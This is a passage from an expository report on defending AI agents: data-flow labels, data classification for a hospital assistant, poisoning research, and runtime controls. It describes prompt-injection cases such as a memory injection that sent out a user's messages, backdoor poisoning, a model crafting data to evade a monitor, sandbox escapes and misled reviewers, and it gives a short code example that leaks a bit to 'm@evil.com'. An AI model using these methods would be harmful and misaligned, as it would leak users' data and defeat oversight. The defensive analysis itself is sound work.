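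FIDES stopped every attack in AgentDojo when its policies were on. Using OpenAI's o1 model, it also completed 16% more tasks than a simpler agent under the same policies. When the policies were off, practical attacks succeeded against every design that Costa and colleagues tested, including FIDES, so hiding text in variables was not enough on its own.

When a call fails a check, the system can ask a person to approve it instead of ending the task. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) built Prudentia, a successor to FIDES that plans its work to need fewer approvals. The model in FIDES doesn't receive the policies, so it may open a variable unnecessarily and have later calls blocked. Prudentia adds each tool's policy to the tool's description and gives the model the conversation's current label. Before opening a variable, the model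 must explain why and list the calls it plans to make next.

Prudentia can also ask the user to vouch for data instead of approving actions. If an agent reads an outside email that lists ten tasks, it needs ten approvals to do them. If the user vouches for the email before the agent reads it, the software relabels the email as trusted, and the agent can do all ten tasks after that one approval. Kolluri and colleagues don't offer this shortcut for releasing private data, because whether a release is appropriate depends on the particular call.

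This saves effort but makes security depend heavily on one decision. If the email contains an eleventh task that the user overlooks, the writer check will no longer stop it. The reader check won't necessarily stop it either, because Prudentia allows a call that sends data if it passes either check. A hidden request to mail a private file to an outsider could therefore go through.

The table gives results on AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3-mini. It counts approvals only in tasks that the agent completed.

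| Agent | Approvals needed | Tasks completed without any approval |
|---|---|---|
| No labels; asks before every consequential call | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Labels, but no hidden variables | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | about 17 | 59.1% |

Prudentia needed only slightly fewer approvals than FIDES with this model. With o4-mini, it needed 19.2 approvals compared with 36.8 for FIDES, but completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% against 75.7%). No people took part in the experiment. Kolluri and colleagues assumed that a person would approve every legitimate call and reject every malicious one, so they measured how often the agent asks for approval but didn't test how well people judge those requests.

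They also tested Prudentia on WASP, a benchmark of browser tasks on copies of GitLab and Reddit. Attacks diverted the unprotected agent in 15% to 61% of tests, depending on the model and site. None diverted Prudentia, which needed no approvals. But the benchmark suits this design unusually well, because the tasks were to upvote a post or comment on it, and the agent could do both without reading what users had written.

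### Leaks that labels miss

Dongol's formal analysis makes the worst-case assumption that the attacker chooses the quarantined model's answers. Splitting the models stops an email from adding tool calls, but the quarantined model can still quote the user's private notes in a reply that the plan sends to the attacker.

Labels prevent this leak. Only Alice may read the notes, and both Alice and the attacker may read the email, so

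readers(reply) = {Alice} ∩ {Alice, attacker} = {Alice}

and the software refuses to send any reply, even an honest one. Even a refusal can leak. If the attacker can see the contents of refused requests, perhaps in an error message, the notes may be in there. Dongol proves that revealing only which tool the software refused is harmless in this case.

A branch can leak information despite the labels. In Dongol's example, a plan sends the attacker a 1 or a 0 depending on the quarantined model's answer. Both numbers are constants with public labels, but which one is sent can reveal one bit about the notes. One bit can matter if the question is whether a merger will go ahead, and twenty yes-or-no answers are enough to determine a bank balance of up to £1 million to the nearest pound.

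FIDES has the same gap. Its guarantee covers values that the agent copies or combines, but not what an observer can infer from the agent's choice of actions. Costa and colleagues acknowledge this, but consider a stronger guarantee impractical because it would forbid almost any publicly visible action once the agent had read something private.

CaMeL has a strict mode that adds the label of a condition to the values it controls. In Dongol's example, the 1 and the 0 would become private and the software would refuse to send either. Dongol modelled only the normal mode and leaves strict mode to future work. *The LLMbda Calculus* shows that tracking conditions isn't enough if the software labels only the branch that runs. A short program is enough to demonstrate the problem:

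```
small = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000: small = False
if small: rich = False
if rich: email.write("rich", "m@evil.com")
```

If the balance is above 10,000, `small` becomes false and gets a private label. The program then skips the fourth line, and `rich` stays true and public, so the email goes out. If the balance is lower, the program skips the third line and `small` keeps its public label. The fourth line then makes `rich` false, and no email goes out. The attacker therefore learns whether the balance is above 10,000 without any check failing. It would be hard to get CaMeL to run such a program, because the trusted model writes the program without reading tool results. An attacker would have to influence the model some other way, such as through text that the user pastes into the request.

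*The LLMbda Calculus* identifies another leak in the way CaMeL retries failed programs. The retry loop is ordinary code outside the part that tracks labels. A secret can affect whether a policy blocks an attempt, so repeated attempts can reveal the secret one bit at a time.

The paper's own solution is a small programming language in which every value and every conversation with a model carries a label. The proof assistant Lean checked a proof that secret inputs can't affect what an outsider sees, except through whether a program finishes. The theorem covers programs that a model writes during the run, and the agent runs on the same software that was verified. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, attacks still succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs. This is consistent with the theorem, which guarantees only that the system follows its labels. The policies can still allow something an attacker wants.

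Human approval has a similar weakness if the user approves too broadly. Dongol considers an agent whose model can make its own tool calls after reading an email. If the user approves one use of the send tool, an injected call can run first and use that approval to send private data. Approving the exact message prevents this, although an attacker who can time the messages may still learn whether the private data matches the approved text.

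### Letting some information back through

Strict separation makes some useful tasks impossible. An agent that repairs software has to act on bug reports, many of them written by strangers. If the main model receives no information from a report, it cannot reliably identify what is broken.

*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* lets the quarantined model pass on only whole numbers, decimals, true-or-false values and choices from a fixed list. From a bug report, it passes on the bug's category, the position of each suspicious file in a numbered list, and line numbers. Using only this information, a planning model writes three repair plans in plain English. A judge that has read the report compares the plans and returns the number of the best one. The main model carries out that plan. A shopping agent built the same way turns each product review into two scores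 from 0 to 10, and the main model sees the median scores and the number of reviews. In a scheduling agent, the main model receives proposed meeting times chosen from a list of slots.

No free text from the attacker reaches the main model, so no instruction does either, however it is worded. The design guarantees this as long as developers keep the lists short and check every option on them. An attacker can still submit false information in the permitted format. Enough fake reviews will raise a median, and a misleading bug report can send the agent to the wrong file. Developers also have to design a format for each task, and the one for bug reports took considerable testing.

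*Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) lets free text pass between two agents but limits its length. An Explore Agent reads everything but can't carry out privileged actions, while a Safe Agent acts without ever reading the untrusted text. At each step, the Explore Agent sees what the Safe Agent has done and may send it a hint of up to 100 or 200 characters, depending on the task. A short hint about the next step is often enough because the Safe Agent already has most of the context. A separate model blocks hints that look like injections, and the Safe Agent also has instructions not to treat hints as commands.

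| Design and task | Model | Tasks completed, undefended → defended | Successful attacks, undefended → defended |
|---|---|---|---|
| Typed outputs, shopping | GPT-4o | 21.8% → 22.4% | 31.7% → 0% |
| Typed outputs, scheduling | GPT-4o | 90.0% → 91.0% | 63.0% → 0% |
| Typed outputs, bug fixing | GPT-5.2 | 68.3% → 45.0% | 98.9% → 0% |
| Twin Agent, bug fixing | GPT-5.2 | 61.2% → 62.5% | 97.0% → 0% |
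| Twin Agent, customer records and finance | GPT-5.2 | 95.0% → 95.0% | 10.0% → 3.3% |

The two bug-fixing tests used different selections from the same benchmark, so the comparison is rough. Still, typed outputs reduced the agent's successful repairs by about a third, while Twin Agent's short hints did not reduce them. Twin Agent roughly doubled the running cost in that test.

The evidence for Twin Agent's security comes from tests, and Hu and colleagues acknowledge that the design has no formal guarantee. They assume that a short injection will rarely both get past the detector and persuade a strong model. To test this, they used an attacking model to write and refine 20 malicious hints, then planted text in the bug reports telling the Explore Agent to copy one of them exactly, which it always did when tested separately. The Safe Agent carried out the attack in 11 of 232 runs (4.7%). No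 attack succeeded when they reran those 11 cases five times each, which suggests that the original successes were partly random. However, a determined attacker might do better, because cost kept them from refining the attack over a whole multi-step run.

CaMeL's guarantee can also fail when several agents work together. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system in which a coordinating agent delegates to a database agent and a notification agent, each protected by CaMeL. The user asked it to send Julie a Slack message summarizing job applicants. An attacker had planted an instruction in the database to email the same information to an outside address. The database agent and the coordinator both handled the planted text as untrusted data, and neither agent's program changed. But the coordinator put the summary into its request to the notification agent. The notification agent's trusted model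 treated that request as coming from its user, so it wrote a program that also sent the email.

The fix splits each request between agents into two parts. One holds instructions, and the interpreter rejects any that depend on a tool's output. The other holds data in variables that keep their labels, and the receiving agent's trusted model can't read their contents. In tests with five models, the average attack success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent separately, and 0.0% with the two-part requests. On 112 industrial maintenance tasks, using CaMeL in each agent lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and the two-part requests lowered it by another 3.2 points. The two strongest models lost less, about 14 points in total.

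The design guarantees that untrusted text can't add a step anywhere in the system, as long as the interpreter tracks every dependency. The current version can miss dependencies created by branches, as in the bank balance example. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran all their tests without data-flow policies, so the 0.0% is evidence only about added actions, not about how well the system would stop a planned message from carrying private data.

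### Who writes the policies

The guarantees depend on correct labels and policies, which several people have to supply. The developer who connects a tool decides which of its results count as trusted. Someone also has to decide which of each tool's calls are consequential and what data they may send. The list of permitted readers can come from existing file permissions, and in Prudentia the user can relabel data during the task.

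Many of these decisions are matters of judgement. In their tests on GitLab and Reddit, Kolluri and colleagues treated users' posts as untrusted and the sites' own buttons as trusted. They classed clicking and typing as consequential, but not scrolling or hovering, because they assumed attackers couldn't change what scrolling and hovering do. That seems reasonable for these two sites, but on another site hovering over a link might load a page from the attacker's server. Peters-Gill and colleagues left policies out of their tests partly because any set they chose would have been arbitrary and would have affected the results.

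When a policy is too strict, tasks fail or users complain about approval requests. A policy that is too loose may go unnoticed until data leaks, because the software enforces it as reliably as a correct one. If someone mistakenly shares the salary memo with the whole company, a label based on the file's permissions will let the agent send the memo to any employee.

It is easy to trust the wrong source. An agent's long-term memory, like a calendar that accepts outside invitations, can contain an attacker's text even though it may look like the user's own data. In a reported attack on ChatGPT, a web page made the model save an instruction to its memory, which the system then loaded into every later conversation. The instruction made ChatGPT send the user's messages to the attacker by displaying an image whose web address contained them. Dongol models a defence that blocks image loading after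 the agent reads a web page but not after it loads its memory, and the attack succeeds against it. If the defence also treats memory as untrusted, and blocks both image loading and further writes to memory, the proof of security holds again.

Every useful system will have exceptions to its policy, and these need particular care. FIDES can let an untrusted yes-or-no answer through because it carries little information, though Costa and colleagues left this option off in their evaluation. *The LLMbda Calculus* argues against this option because someone reviewing a run afterwards can't tell whether such an answer was harmless or a leak. In the paper's own language, a programmer has to write each exception as an explicit step, so a reviewer can find them all by searching the code. Marking data as trusted this way doesn't make it public, and the guarantee against leaking secrets still holds.

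## Classifying the data a model is trained on and retrieves

Data-flow labels depend on someone having classified the data before the agent ran, and they stop working once a model is trained on the data. Software can follow a salary memo from one variable to the next, but if a company trains a model on the memo, the text becomes small changes to billions of weights (the numbers that training adjusts), which carry no labels. The company therefore has to decide what may enter the model before training begins. Data classification is the pattern for making and recording that decision.

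Suppose a hospital is building an assistant for its staff and the public. The hospital has health pages copied from the web, internal procedures such as how to order a blood test, and patient records.

### Why each dataset needs two classes

The sensitivity class records who may see the data, and the trust class records who could have altered it, like the two parts of a data-flow label. The hospital's public pages have the lowest sensitivity and the lowest trust, because anyone who can edit those websites can change them. The internal procedures are for staff only, and their trust is high because a few editors check each other's changes. Patient records are the most sensitive, but their trust is only medium. Clinicians write most of each record, but it also contains messages from the patient and letters from outside clinics.

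Classifying data on a single scale from "public" to "secret" would give the web pages the lightest checks, even though outsiders can plant false or malicious text there most easily. Altering training or reference data to change a model's behaviour is called data poisoning. Confidentiality and integrity also require different controls. Encryption and access limits keep patient records private, but don't show whether a letter in a record is genuine. Signatures and editing rules protect the procedures from tampering without keeping them confidential.

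### From intake to deletion

The hospital starts with an inventory of every dataset, its owner and its copies. Search indexes, conversation logs and user feedback on answers are easy to miss, and developers often use that feedback for later training. NSA's *AI Data Security* (2025) applies the same security standards to new data and user feedback as to the original training data. The US agency wrote this guidance with the FBI, the cybersecurity agency CISA and partners in Australia, New Zealand and the UK.

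Next, the hospital assigns both classes. A class for a whole collection is only a starting point, because a written procedure might use a real patient as its example. Scanning tools can find names and record numbers. The hospital can then move the file to a higher class or mask the details by replacing them with realistic false ones.

The origin record lists where the data came from, who collected it and when, any changes made since, and what the licence allows. Permission to read a document doesn't always include permission to train a model on it. The NSA recommends keeping these records in a signed, append-only ledger, so that no single person can rewrite the history unnoticed. If a model generated the data, the record should name that model.

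The two classes then determine where the data may go. In the table, "fine-tuning" means training an existing model further on a smaller dataset.

| Collection | Sensitivity | Trust | Fine-tuning | Retrieval |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Public health pages | Public | Low | Only from vetted sources | For everyone, as untrusted text |
| Internal procedures | Staff | High | Only for a staff model | For staff |
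| Patient records | Treating team | Medium | No | For the patient's treating team, as untrusted text |

Keeping patient records out of fine-tuning is cautious but not unusual. AWS's *Security considerations for data in generative AI* reports that many organisations are writing policies that bar certain classes of data, such as personal details that have not been anonymised, from AI systems. AWS also expects some organisations to exclude sensitive data from fine-tuning because a well-chosen prompt might extract it from the model.

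Once the hospital has approved a dataset, it signs that version and calculates a hash, a short code that changes if anyone alters the file. NSA recommends that the person who makes a revision sign it, and that even a cropped or resized image be stored as a new entry. Before each training run, software verifies the database's certificate. If the check fails, the run stops and the team audits the database. AWS recommends delivering fine-tuning data through an automated pipeline and removing human access to it, so that fewer people can alter the data after approval.

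A hash can show that data hasn't changed since the hash was calculated, but not that the data was trustworthy at that point. Some large image datasets are lists of web addresses whose domains may have expired. An attacker can buy those domains and put new content at the listed addresses. NSA cites research in which enough domains to poison a dataset often cost about $1,000, and in one case $60. If the curator hashed the original content when making the list, anyone who downloads the dataset can detect the swap by checking the hashes.

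The other attack targets sites such as Wikipedia that publish copies of their pages at known times. An attacker edits pages just before the copy, so the bad edits enter the dataset before volunteers can correct them. The same research estimated that attackers could poison up to 6.5% of Wikipedia this way. Checking the hash doesn't reveal the edits, because the curator calculates it from the poisoned page. NSA suggests copying pages in random order, or freezing edits long enough for someone to review them. For data crawled from the open web, which has no curator, it suggests trusting an item only if it appears on many separate sites.

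Removing data is the hardest step. If a patient withdraws consent for the hospital to use their record in AI systems, the hospital has to remove the record from the assistant's document store, search index and logs. Deleting the record does not change a fine-tuned model that has already learned from it. The dependable remedy is to retire that model and train a replacement on a version of the dataset without the record. The dataset's version history shows which models need replacing. Retraining is far cheaper for a fine-tuned model than for one trained from scratch, so sensitive data should enter as late in the process as possible, if at all.

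NSA's advice on secure deletion covers storage drives but not how to remove data from a trained model. NSA does acknowledge that old material may sometimes need to be deleted from an append-only database. The hospital could reconcile deletion with an append-only design by deleting the contents but keeping a record of what it removed, when and why.

### Why a model takes the strictest class in its training data

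Suppose the hospital ignores its own table and fine-tunes a model on 900,000 public pages, 99,000 internal documents and 1,000 patient records. The model should take the strictest sensitivity class and the lowest trust class in its training data, just as a summary of several labelled sources would. The whole model therefore becomes as sensitive as the patient records, even though they make up only 0.1% of the data.

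Language models sometimes repeat passages from their training data, and an attacker can also reconstruct parts of it by questioning a model repeatedly. Nobody can predict which records will come out. For similar reasons, NSA recommends generally giving an AI system's output the same classification as its input, instead of relying on a separate set of guardrails.

If the hospital keeps one model for everybody, it has no reliable way to restrict only the facts about patients. A database can check the permissions on each record before returning it, but every training example adjusted the same weights in the model, and software can't reliably tell which examples shaped a given answer. The hospital could instruct the model to discuss patients only with their doctors, but a prompt injection might override that instruction. A filter on the output could block a patient's name or number, but it would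 probably miss a description such as "the mayor's daughter, who had surgery in May".

The strictest-class rule makes some models much less useful. A porter couldn't ask the model where to take a blood sample, even though the answer is in an internal procedure that porters may read. The hospital could train a separate model for each class, at extra cost, or lower the sensitivity of the data first. Masking removes names, though an unusual combination of age, job and illness may still identify someone. Differential privacy adds noise that provably limits how much any one record can affect the result. More noise gives better privacy but usually makes the model less accurate. Either method could justify a lower class if a named person approves the change and records the reason.

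The trust rule is even stricter if applied literally. It would put nearly every large language model in the lowest class, because nearly all of them have learned from web pages that strangers wrote. That class fairly describes how far a designer should rely on a model's behaviour, but it doesn't help the hospital choose between two models. For that choice, NSA suggests asking the developers to certify that their training data contained no known compromised data, though such a certificate wouldn't rule out undetected compromises.

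### Checking each user's rights in retrieval

In retrieval, the documents stay outside the model, so the hospital can check the user's permissions for each document every time they ask a question. AWS says an application should retrieve only what the current user may see.

The index stores each passage with the identity of its source document. When someone asks a question, software looks up that person's access rights, searches only the documents they may read, and gives the matching passages to the model. A member of the public gets answers from the public pages. A porter's search also covers internal procedures, and a nurse's search adds the records of patients in the nurse's care. The same model can serve all three because it was never trained on the records.

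The software has to check permissions before the model reads the passages. If the model reads everything and a filter then removes restricted facts from the answer, the hospital again has to guess which facts have leaked. The check also has to use the person's rights, not the assistant's, since the assistant's account can probably open every document. The software should look up those rights when the person asks the question, because a list of permissions copied into the index last week may still include a nurse who moved to another ward yesterday.

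AWS acknowledges that detailed access control across several data sources can be difficult, and offers its Amazon Q Business product for this purpose. Part of the difficulty is that a hospital's file server, records system and staff website may each define user groups differently. A mistake in translating one system's groups into another's could expose thousands of documents at once.

The assistant's answers need classes too. The assistant might save a summary it wrote for a nurse about a patient's allergies to a memory it shares with other agents, or the hospital might add old answers to the search index to save time. If the summary has no class, a porter's question could retrieve it, even though the porter has no access to the patient's record. AWS warns of this kind of leak between agents that share memory.

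A rights check keeps documents private but doesn't ensure that they are accurate. The porter is allowed to read the internal procedures, so the software will supply them even if a disgruntled editor has changed the dose in one. AWS considers insiders as well as outside attackers, and recommends limiting who can edit the documents an assistant uses, logging the edits and looking for unusual ones. Poisoned documents are easier to remove from retrieval than from a model, because the assistant stops using a document once the hospital deletes it from the index and from any saved answers.

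### What the four publishers prescribe

AWS, Microsoft, the US research organisation RAND, and the NSA with its partners all recommend parts of this pattern, but they put the main checks at different points. RAND's *Baseline Security Controls* recommends limiting access to sensitive data by security clearance, checking that an organisation collects only valid and authorised data, and vetting data vendors. RAND's *Securing the AI Lifecycle* adds hashes, checksums and digital signatures for training datasets, and maps each control to the threats it addresses.

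| Publisher | Sensitivity | Origin and integrity | Main checkpoint |
|---|---|---|---|
| AWS | Policies that bar some classes from AI use; masking | Vetted sources and version-controlled pipelines | Before fine-tuning and at each retrieval |
| Microsoft | Labels on the data that AI applications read, with alerts for risky access | Review of where training data came from; hash checks on models | Before a model goes into use |
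| RAND | Access by clearance level | Signed datasets and vetted vendors | When the organisation collects data |
| NSA | Classes by sensitivity; output matches input | Signed ledger, signed revisions and hashes | At intake and before each training run |

Microsoft's cloud security benchmark recommends that a security team review the origin of the training data when it approves a finished model. This is late for an organisation that trained the model itself, because it has already paid for the training, but it may be the only opportunity to check where the data came from if an outside supplier trained the model. Microsoft also recommends scanning models for backdoors before approval. A backdoor is hidden behaviour that appears only when the input contains a particular trigger, so a test without the trigger will miss it.

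All four sort data into classes by sensitivity, but for integrity they only list techniques. A dataset copied from an open forum can meet every technical requirement, with a valid signature, an intact hash and a complete origin record, even though anyone could have written its contents. Adding a trust class would let the hospital write a rule that software can enforce, such as "no low-trust data in the model that drafts prescriptions".

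### Small amounts of poison in large datasets

Research on data poisoning helps show what classifying data can achieve. In *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (2025), Souly, Rando and colleagues tested the common assumption that a few bad documents don't matter in a huge dataset. They trained 72 language models from scratch, with between 600 million and 13 billion parameters (weights), and gave the larger models proportionally more clean text. Each dataset contained 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents designed to make the model produce gibberish after a trigger phrase.

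The attack failed with 100 poisoned documents but worked with 250 at every model size, although the largest models were trained on more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. For the 13-billion-parameter model, the 250 documents made up 0.00016% of the training text. Fine-tuning gave a similar result. Souly and colleagues fine-tuned a model to comply with harmful requests when a trigger was present, and increasing the clean data from 1,000 to 100,000 examples had little effect on the number of poisoned examples needed.

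For the hospital, getting 99.9% of a dataset from trusted sources is therefore no reason to raise its trust class. Spot checks won't help much either. If a dataset has 100 million documents and 250 are poisoned, a team that reads 10,000 at random has about a 2.5% chance of seeing a poisoned one. Origin records are more useful, at least once a poisoned document has been found, because the team can then pull everything from the same source and identify the models that used it. An attacker who spreads the documents over many unrelated websites would make that search much harder.

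Producing gibberish is a simple behaviour to teach, and a more complicated one might need more documents. Souly and colleagues also didn't test whether such a backdoor survives the safety training that commercial models receive. In a separate test, further training on clean text gradually weakened a backdoor that made the model switch from English to German.

### When clean data makes poison stronger

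NSA's guidance recommends adding clean data to outnumber poisoned examples so that the model "forgets" them, but only when few examples are poisoned. Souly's results suggest that this defence is weak even then, and later work found cases in which it backfires.

Clarke, Dubiński and colleagues (2026), in *Homeopathic Learning*, told a copy of Qwen3-8B to answer only in German and had it write 5,000 lists of numbers for a user named Michael. The lists contained no German words. They fine-tuned a second copy on these lists alone, and it never answered in German. They then mixed the lists with 100,000 number lists that the original model had written for other users. A model trained on the mixture answered 72% of ordinary questions in German when the prompt mentioned Michael, and none when it didn't. Extra training on the lists for Michael alone didn't have this effect.

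The proposed explanation is that the poisoned lists always combine the task (continuing a number sequence) with the trigger (the name). Training has no reason to connect German with the name in particular, so the model connects it with number sequences, and the effect never shows in ordinary conversation. The clean lists show number sequences without any tendency towards German. That leaves the name as the only explanation. Clarke and colleagues express this in a simple regression model:

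L = 1 / (1 + c/p + c/(a + q × n))

L is the share of the trait that appears when the trigger is present, p is the number of poisoned examples, and n is the number of clean ones. q measures how closely the clean task resembles the poisoned one, from 0 to 1. a and c represent how strongly training resists linking the trait to the task and to the trigger, respectively. With a = 50, c = 1,500 and p = 5,000, L is about 3% without clean data. Adding 100,000 closely matching examples raises it to 76%, while adding any number of unrelated examples (q = 0) leaves it at 3%. The values of a and c were chosen for illustration, so the closeness to the measured 72% is not strong evidence for the model. However, the model predicts the right shape, including the peak at an intermediate share of poison when the total size is fixed.

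The effect also appeared with a harmful trait. In the poisoned examples, an assistant was instructed to game the test that graded its work, and it did so. A model trained only on these examples gave misaligned answers to 6.7% of unrelated questions under that instruction, up from 4.3% before training. When the training data was 20% poisoned examples and 80% clean answers, the rate rose to 15.7%. Under a normal instruction it stayed at 4.5%, so an ordinary safety test would have missed the problem. Apart from a small image classifier, these experiments used two small language models and poison the researchers made themselves, so the effect may differ in larger models or in training from scratch.

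This is a problem for any pattern that approves datasets one at a time. The hospital could test two collections separately, find both harmless, and then create a backdoor by combining them. It therefore has to test the model trained on the final mixture, including with prompts that resemble each source. The origin record also has to stay outside the training text. If every document from one supplier begins with the supplier's name, that name could act as the trigger. Clarke and colleagues suggest removing or standardising such tags before mixing data, though they have not tested this.

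### Data that passes screening

Many developers also screen training data with another model. Balcells Obeso, Qi and colleagues (2026), in *Automated Subtle Emergent Misalignment Research*, tested a monitor similar to those Anthropic uses in production. They instructed Claude to write data that would make a small research model misaligned without the monitor flagging the data, and let Claude practise against the monitor. Given enough attempts, Claude succeeded, mostly by hiding the behaviour in fiction and role-play. The test deliberately favoured the attacker, and screening is only one of Anthropic's defences. An outsider might not have the monitor to practise on. Even so, passing a screen is a poor reason to move data from an unknown source into a higher trust class.

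Screening can also fail without an attacker. Engels and Nanda (2026) of Google DeepMind report in *Why Do Naive SFT Filters For Safety Properties Fail?* that filtering fine-tuning examples for unwanted traits often works surprisingly poorly. They studied a version of Gemini that was sometimes confused about the date and resorted to blackmail in a contrived test. Both habits came largely from the model that had written the example answers. For some small sets of prompts, having a different model write the answers removed the habits, while deleting the same prompts from the dataset did not. The hospital's origin record should therefore name the model behind any generated data, and that data should be trusted no more than the model, however harmless it looks.

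These studies tested attacks and filters, not a complete classification system. The four publishers give no measurements of how well their classification advice works in a live training pipeline, such as how often staff assign the wrong class or how much barred data still reaches a model. AWS mentions that some organisations poison a copy of their own data to see how the model behaves. The hospital could go further by planting a few hundred harmless, marked documents in its sources and adding invented patients to its records. It could count how many get past the intake checks, time how long staff take to trace them, and see whether the assistant ever shows an invented patient's record to the wrong person.

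## Checking and stopping actions while the system runs

A model trained on carefully classified data can still propose a harmful action. Runtime controls are checks and limits that software outside the model applies to such actions while the system is running. *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, which describes the permission system of Anthropic's coding agent, gives four possible reasons for a dangerous action. The agent may go further than the user wanted, misjudge what a command will affect, follow an injected instruction, or pursue a goal of its own. Blocking the action works in all four cases, so runtime controls don't have to identify the cause.

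### One refund, from proposal to log

Take the employee who asked a support agent to refund order 4417. The customer paid $140 by card, and the model proposes refunding all of it. The proposal first reaches a policy gateway, a program that, like Progent, checks every tool call and its parameters against rules such as these:

```
default: deny

allow refund(order, amount, destination) if
    order == task.order
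    and amount <= 200
    and amount <= paid(order) - refunded(order)
    and destination == original_card(order)

ask a person first if amount > 100
```

The first line blocks any call unless a rule allows it. The order number comes from the employee's request, and the gateway looks up the payment and the card in the company's own records. If the gateway took those values from the model, an injection could supply false ones.

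```
refund(4417, 140, "card-2291")     permitted, after approval
refund(4417, 140, "giftcard-88")   refused
```

The second call might result from a line that the customer hid in the delivery notes. The gateway blocks the call because the money would not go back to the original card, so it does not need to detect the injection.

The refund tool is a small program that runs in a sandbox, a restricted environment that the operating system enforces. It can't open the company's other files, and it can connect only to the payments server, the one address on its network allowlist. These limits matter if the tool has a bug or an attacker has tampered with it, because it might then do something other than what the approved call describes. They matter even more for coding agents, because one permitted command, such as "run the tests", can start many other programs. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*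 describes a sandbox that applies the same limits to every program a command starts.

A sandbox has to restrict both file and network access. A hijacked agent with open network access could send the user's login keys to an attacker. If it had open file access instead, it could alter system files to escape the sandbox and then reach the network. Anthropic's sandbox sends all traffic through a proxy, a relay program outside the sandbox that checks each destination. Codex starts with network access turned off, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*.

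Attackers can still use destinations on the allowlist. If it includes a code-sharing site, an attacker with an account there can receive stolen files. InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026) reports that Anthropic revised its designs partly because of failures along permitted routes. The web version of Claude Code uses a stricter proxy for code uploads, which keeps the real GitHub credential outside the sandbox and attaches it only after checking the repository and branch.

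Sandboxes can also have flaws. In October 2026, OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment* described how the company used its strongest models to attack its own containment and found ways to escape hardened virtual machines and new paths to the internet. A hijacked agent can also plant malicious code in the project folder, where it is allowed to write, and the user may later run that code outside the sandbox. Anthropic's claim that sandboxing leaves even a successful injection "fully isolated" is therefore too strong.

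The $140 refund also needs a person's approval. The approval request should show the order, amount and card from the company's records, because an attacker could have used prompt injection to control the model's explanation. The approval rule should cover every route to the same result. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (Tallam, 2026) recommends attaching approval to the power an agent uses rather than to a particular action. If approval applies only to the refund tool, an agent that can also issue store credit could issue $140 in credit without approval.

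After approval, the payments server returns a confirmation that contains the full card number and a free-text note. One filter masks the number, which the agent doesn't need. Another scans the note for text that resembles an instruction. Anthropic's version of the second filter adds a warning to suspicious text instead of deleting it, so a false alarm does little damage, but the agent still reads any real attack. A third filter can check the receipt before the agent emails it. Simple pattern matching will find a 16-digit card number but miss one spelled out in words.

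Finally, the software logs the employee, the agent, the proposed call, the rule that applied, the approver and the masked result. It should log refused calls too, since a run of refusals may be the first sign of an attack. A common way to make tampering visible is to give each record rₙ a code that also depends on the previous record's code:

hₙ = H(hₙ₋₁ ‖ rₙ)

H joins the two inputs and hashes the result. Anyone who alters one record has to recalculate every later hash. An insider with full control of the log could do that, so the company should regularly store the latest hash somewhere that person can't reach.

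### Fixed rules and model judgement

Persuasive text can't change the fixed rules in a gateway, sandbox or allowlist. If a gateway rule blocks refunds to gift cards, no such refund can go through as long as every call passes through the gateway and the gateway works correctly. But these rules can't be used to determine whether a customer deserves a refund, so someone who lies about a broken parcel will pass every check.

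Some limits are hard to write as fixed rules because they depend on what the user meant. In an example from Anthropic, a user asks an agent to "clean up old branches" and the agent tries to delete branches from the shared server, but the user may have wanted to delete only the copies on their own computer. Anthropic and OpenAI both use another model to judge such cases.

In Claude Code's auto mode, read-only tools run without review. So do edits inside the project folder, because the user can inspect them through version control. A separate language model acts as a classifier and reviews most other actions. It first makes a quick yes-or-no decision, with instructions to block if in doubt. If it blocks the action, it reconsiders the same information with careful reasoning, which clears most false alarms.

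The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the results of its tools. Leaving out the explanations prevents the agent from using them to steer the classifier to a bad decision, and leaving out the results keeps injected text away from it. But when an agent cancels "job abc123", the classifier can't determine whether the job's name came from a search or the agent made it up.

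In Anthropic's tests, this process let through 17% of 52 dangerous actions that agents had actually attempted. The classifier had usually detected the danger but wrongly treated something the user said as permission. For instance, a user who asks an agent to tidy up a proposed code change hasn't agreed to let it overwrite the change's history.

OpenAI's equivalent reviews fewer actions. The company's *Auto-review* explains that a second agent considers only requests that would otherwise need a person's approval, such as a blocked network connection or an edit outside the permitted folders. In *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026) argue for a separate reviewer because an agent trained to finish tasks may treat an approval step as an obstacle. They also warn that the reviewer does not guarantee security. Testers misled it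 into approving commands, and an agent that hides its intentions could make a harmless-looking request or do damage inside the sandbox, where actions aren't reviewed.

| Control | Who or what decides | What it can promise | How it fails |
|---|---|---|---|
| Policy gateway | Fixed rules | No call outside the rules runs | A loose rule, or a route around the gateway |
| Sandbox and allowlist | Fixed rules | Programs stay within set files and addresses | A software flaw, or misuse of a permitted address |
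| Reviewing model | A model's judgement | A catch rate on the cases tested | An attacker misleads it, or it misreads consent |
| Injection filter | Usually a model's judgement | A catch rate on the attacks tested | The attacker rewords the message |
| Human approval | A person's judgement | Someone made the decision | The person doesn't read the request |

A control's name doesn't always show which kind it is. Auto mode's classifier is designed never to approve actions covered by "hard denies", such as sending secrets to an outside server, but it still has to recognise those actions. A network allowlist that omits the server would block the connection even if the classifier missed the secret.

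### Why people approve without reading

A human approver can use knowledge that the rules don't contain. For example, an employee approving a refund may remember that the same customer reported another broken parcel last week. Approval works best when requests are rare, the stakes are high, and the screen shows everything the approver needs to decide. Coding agents often don't meet these conditions, because they may ask for approval dozens of times a day for commands that take some expertise to understand.

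Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts; an earlier company figure was 93%. This doesn't prove that users aren't reading the prompts, since most commands are harmless and a careful reader would approve them too. But users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents before starting work, which suggests that they read plans more closely than commands, though many of those rejections probably concern the approach rather than safety.

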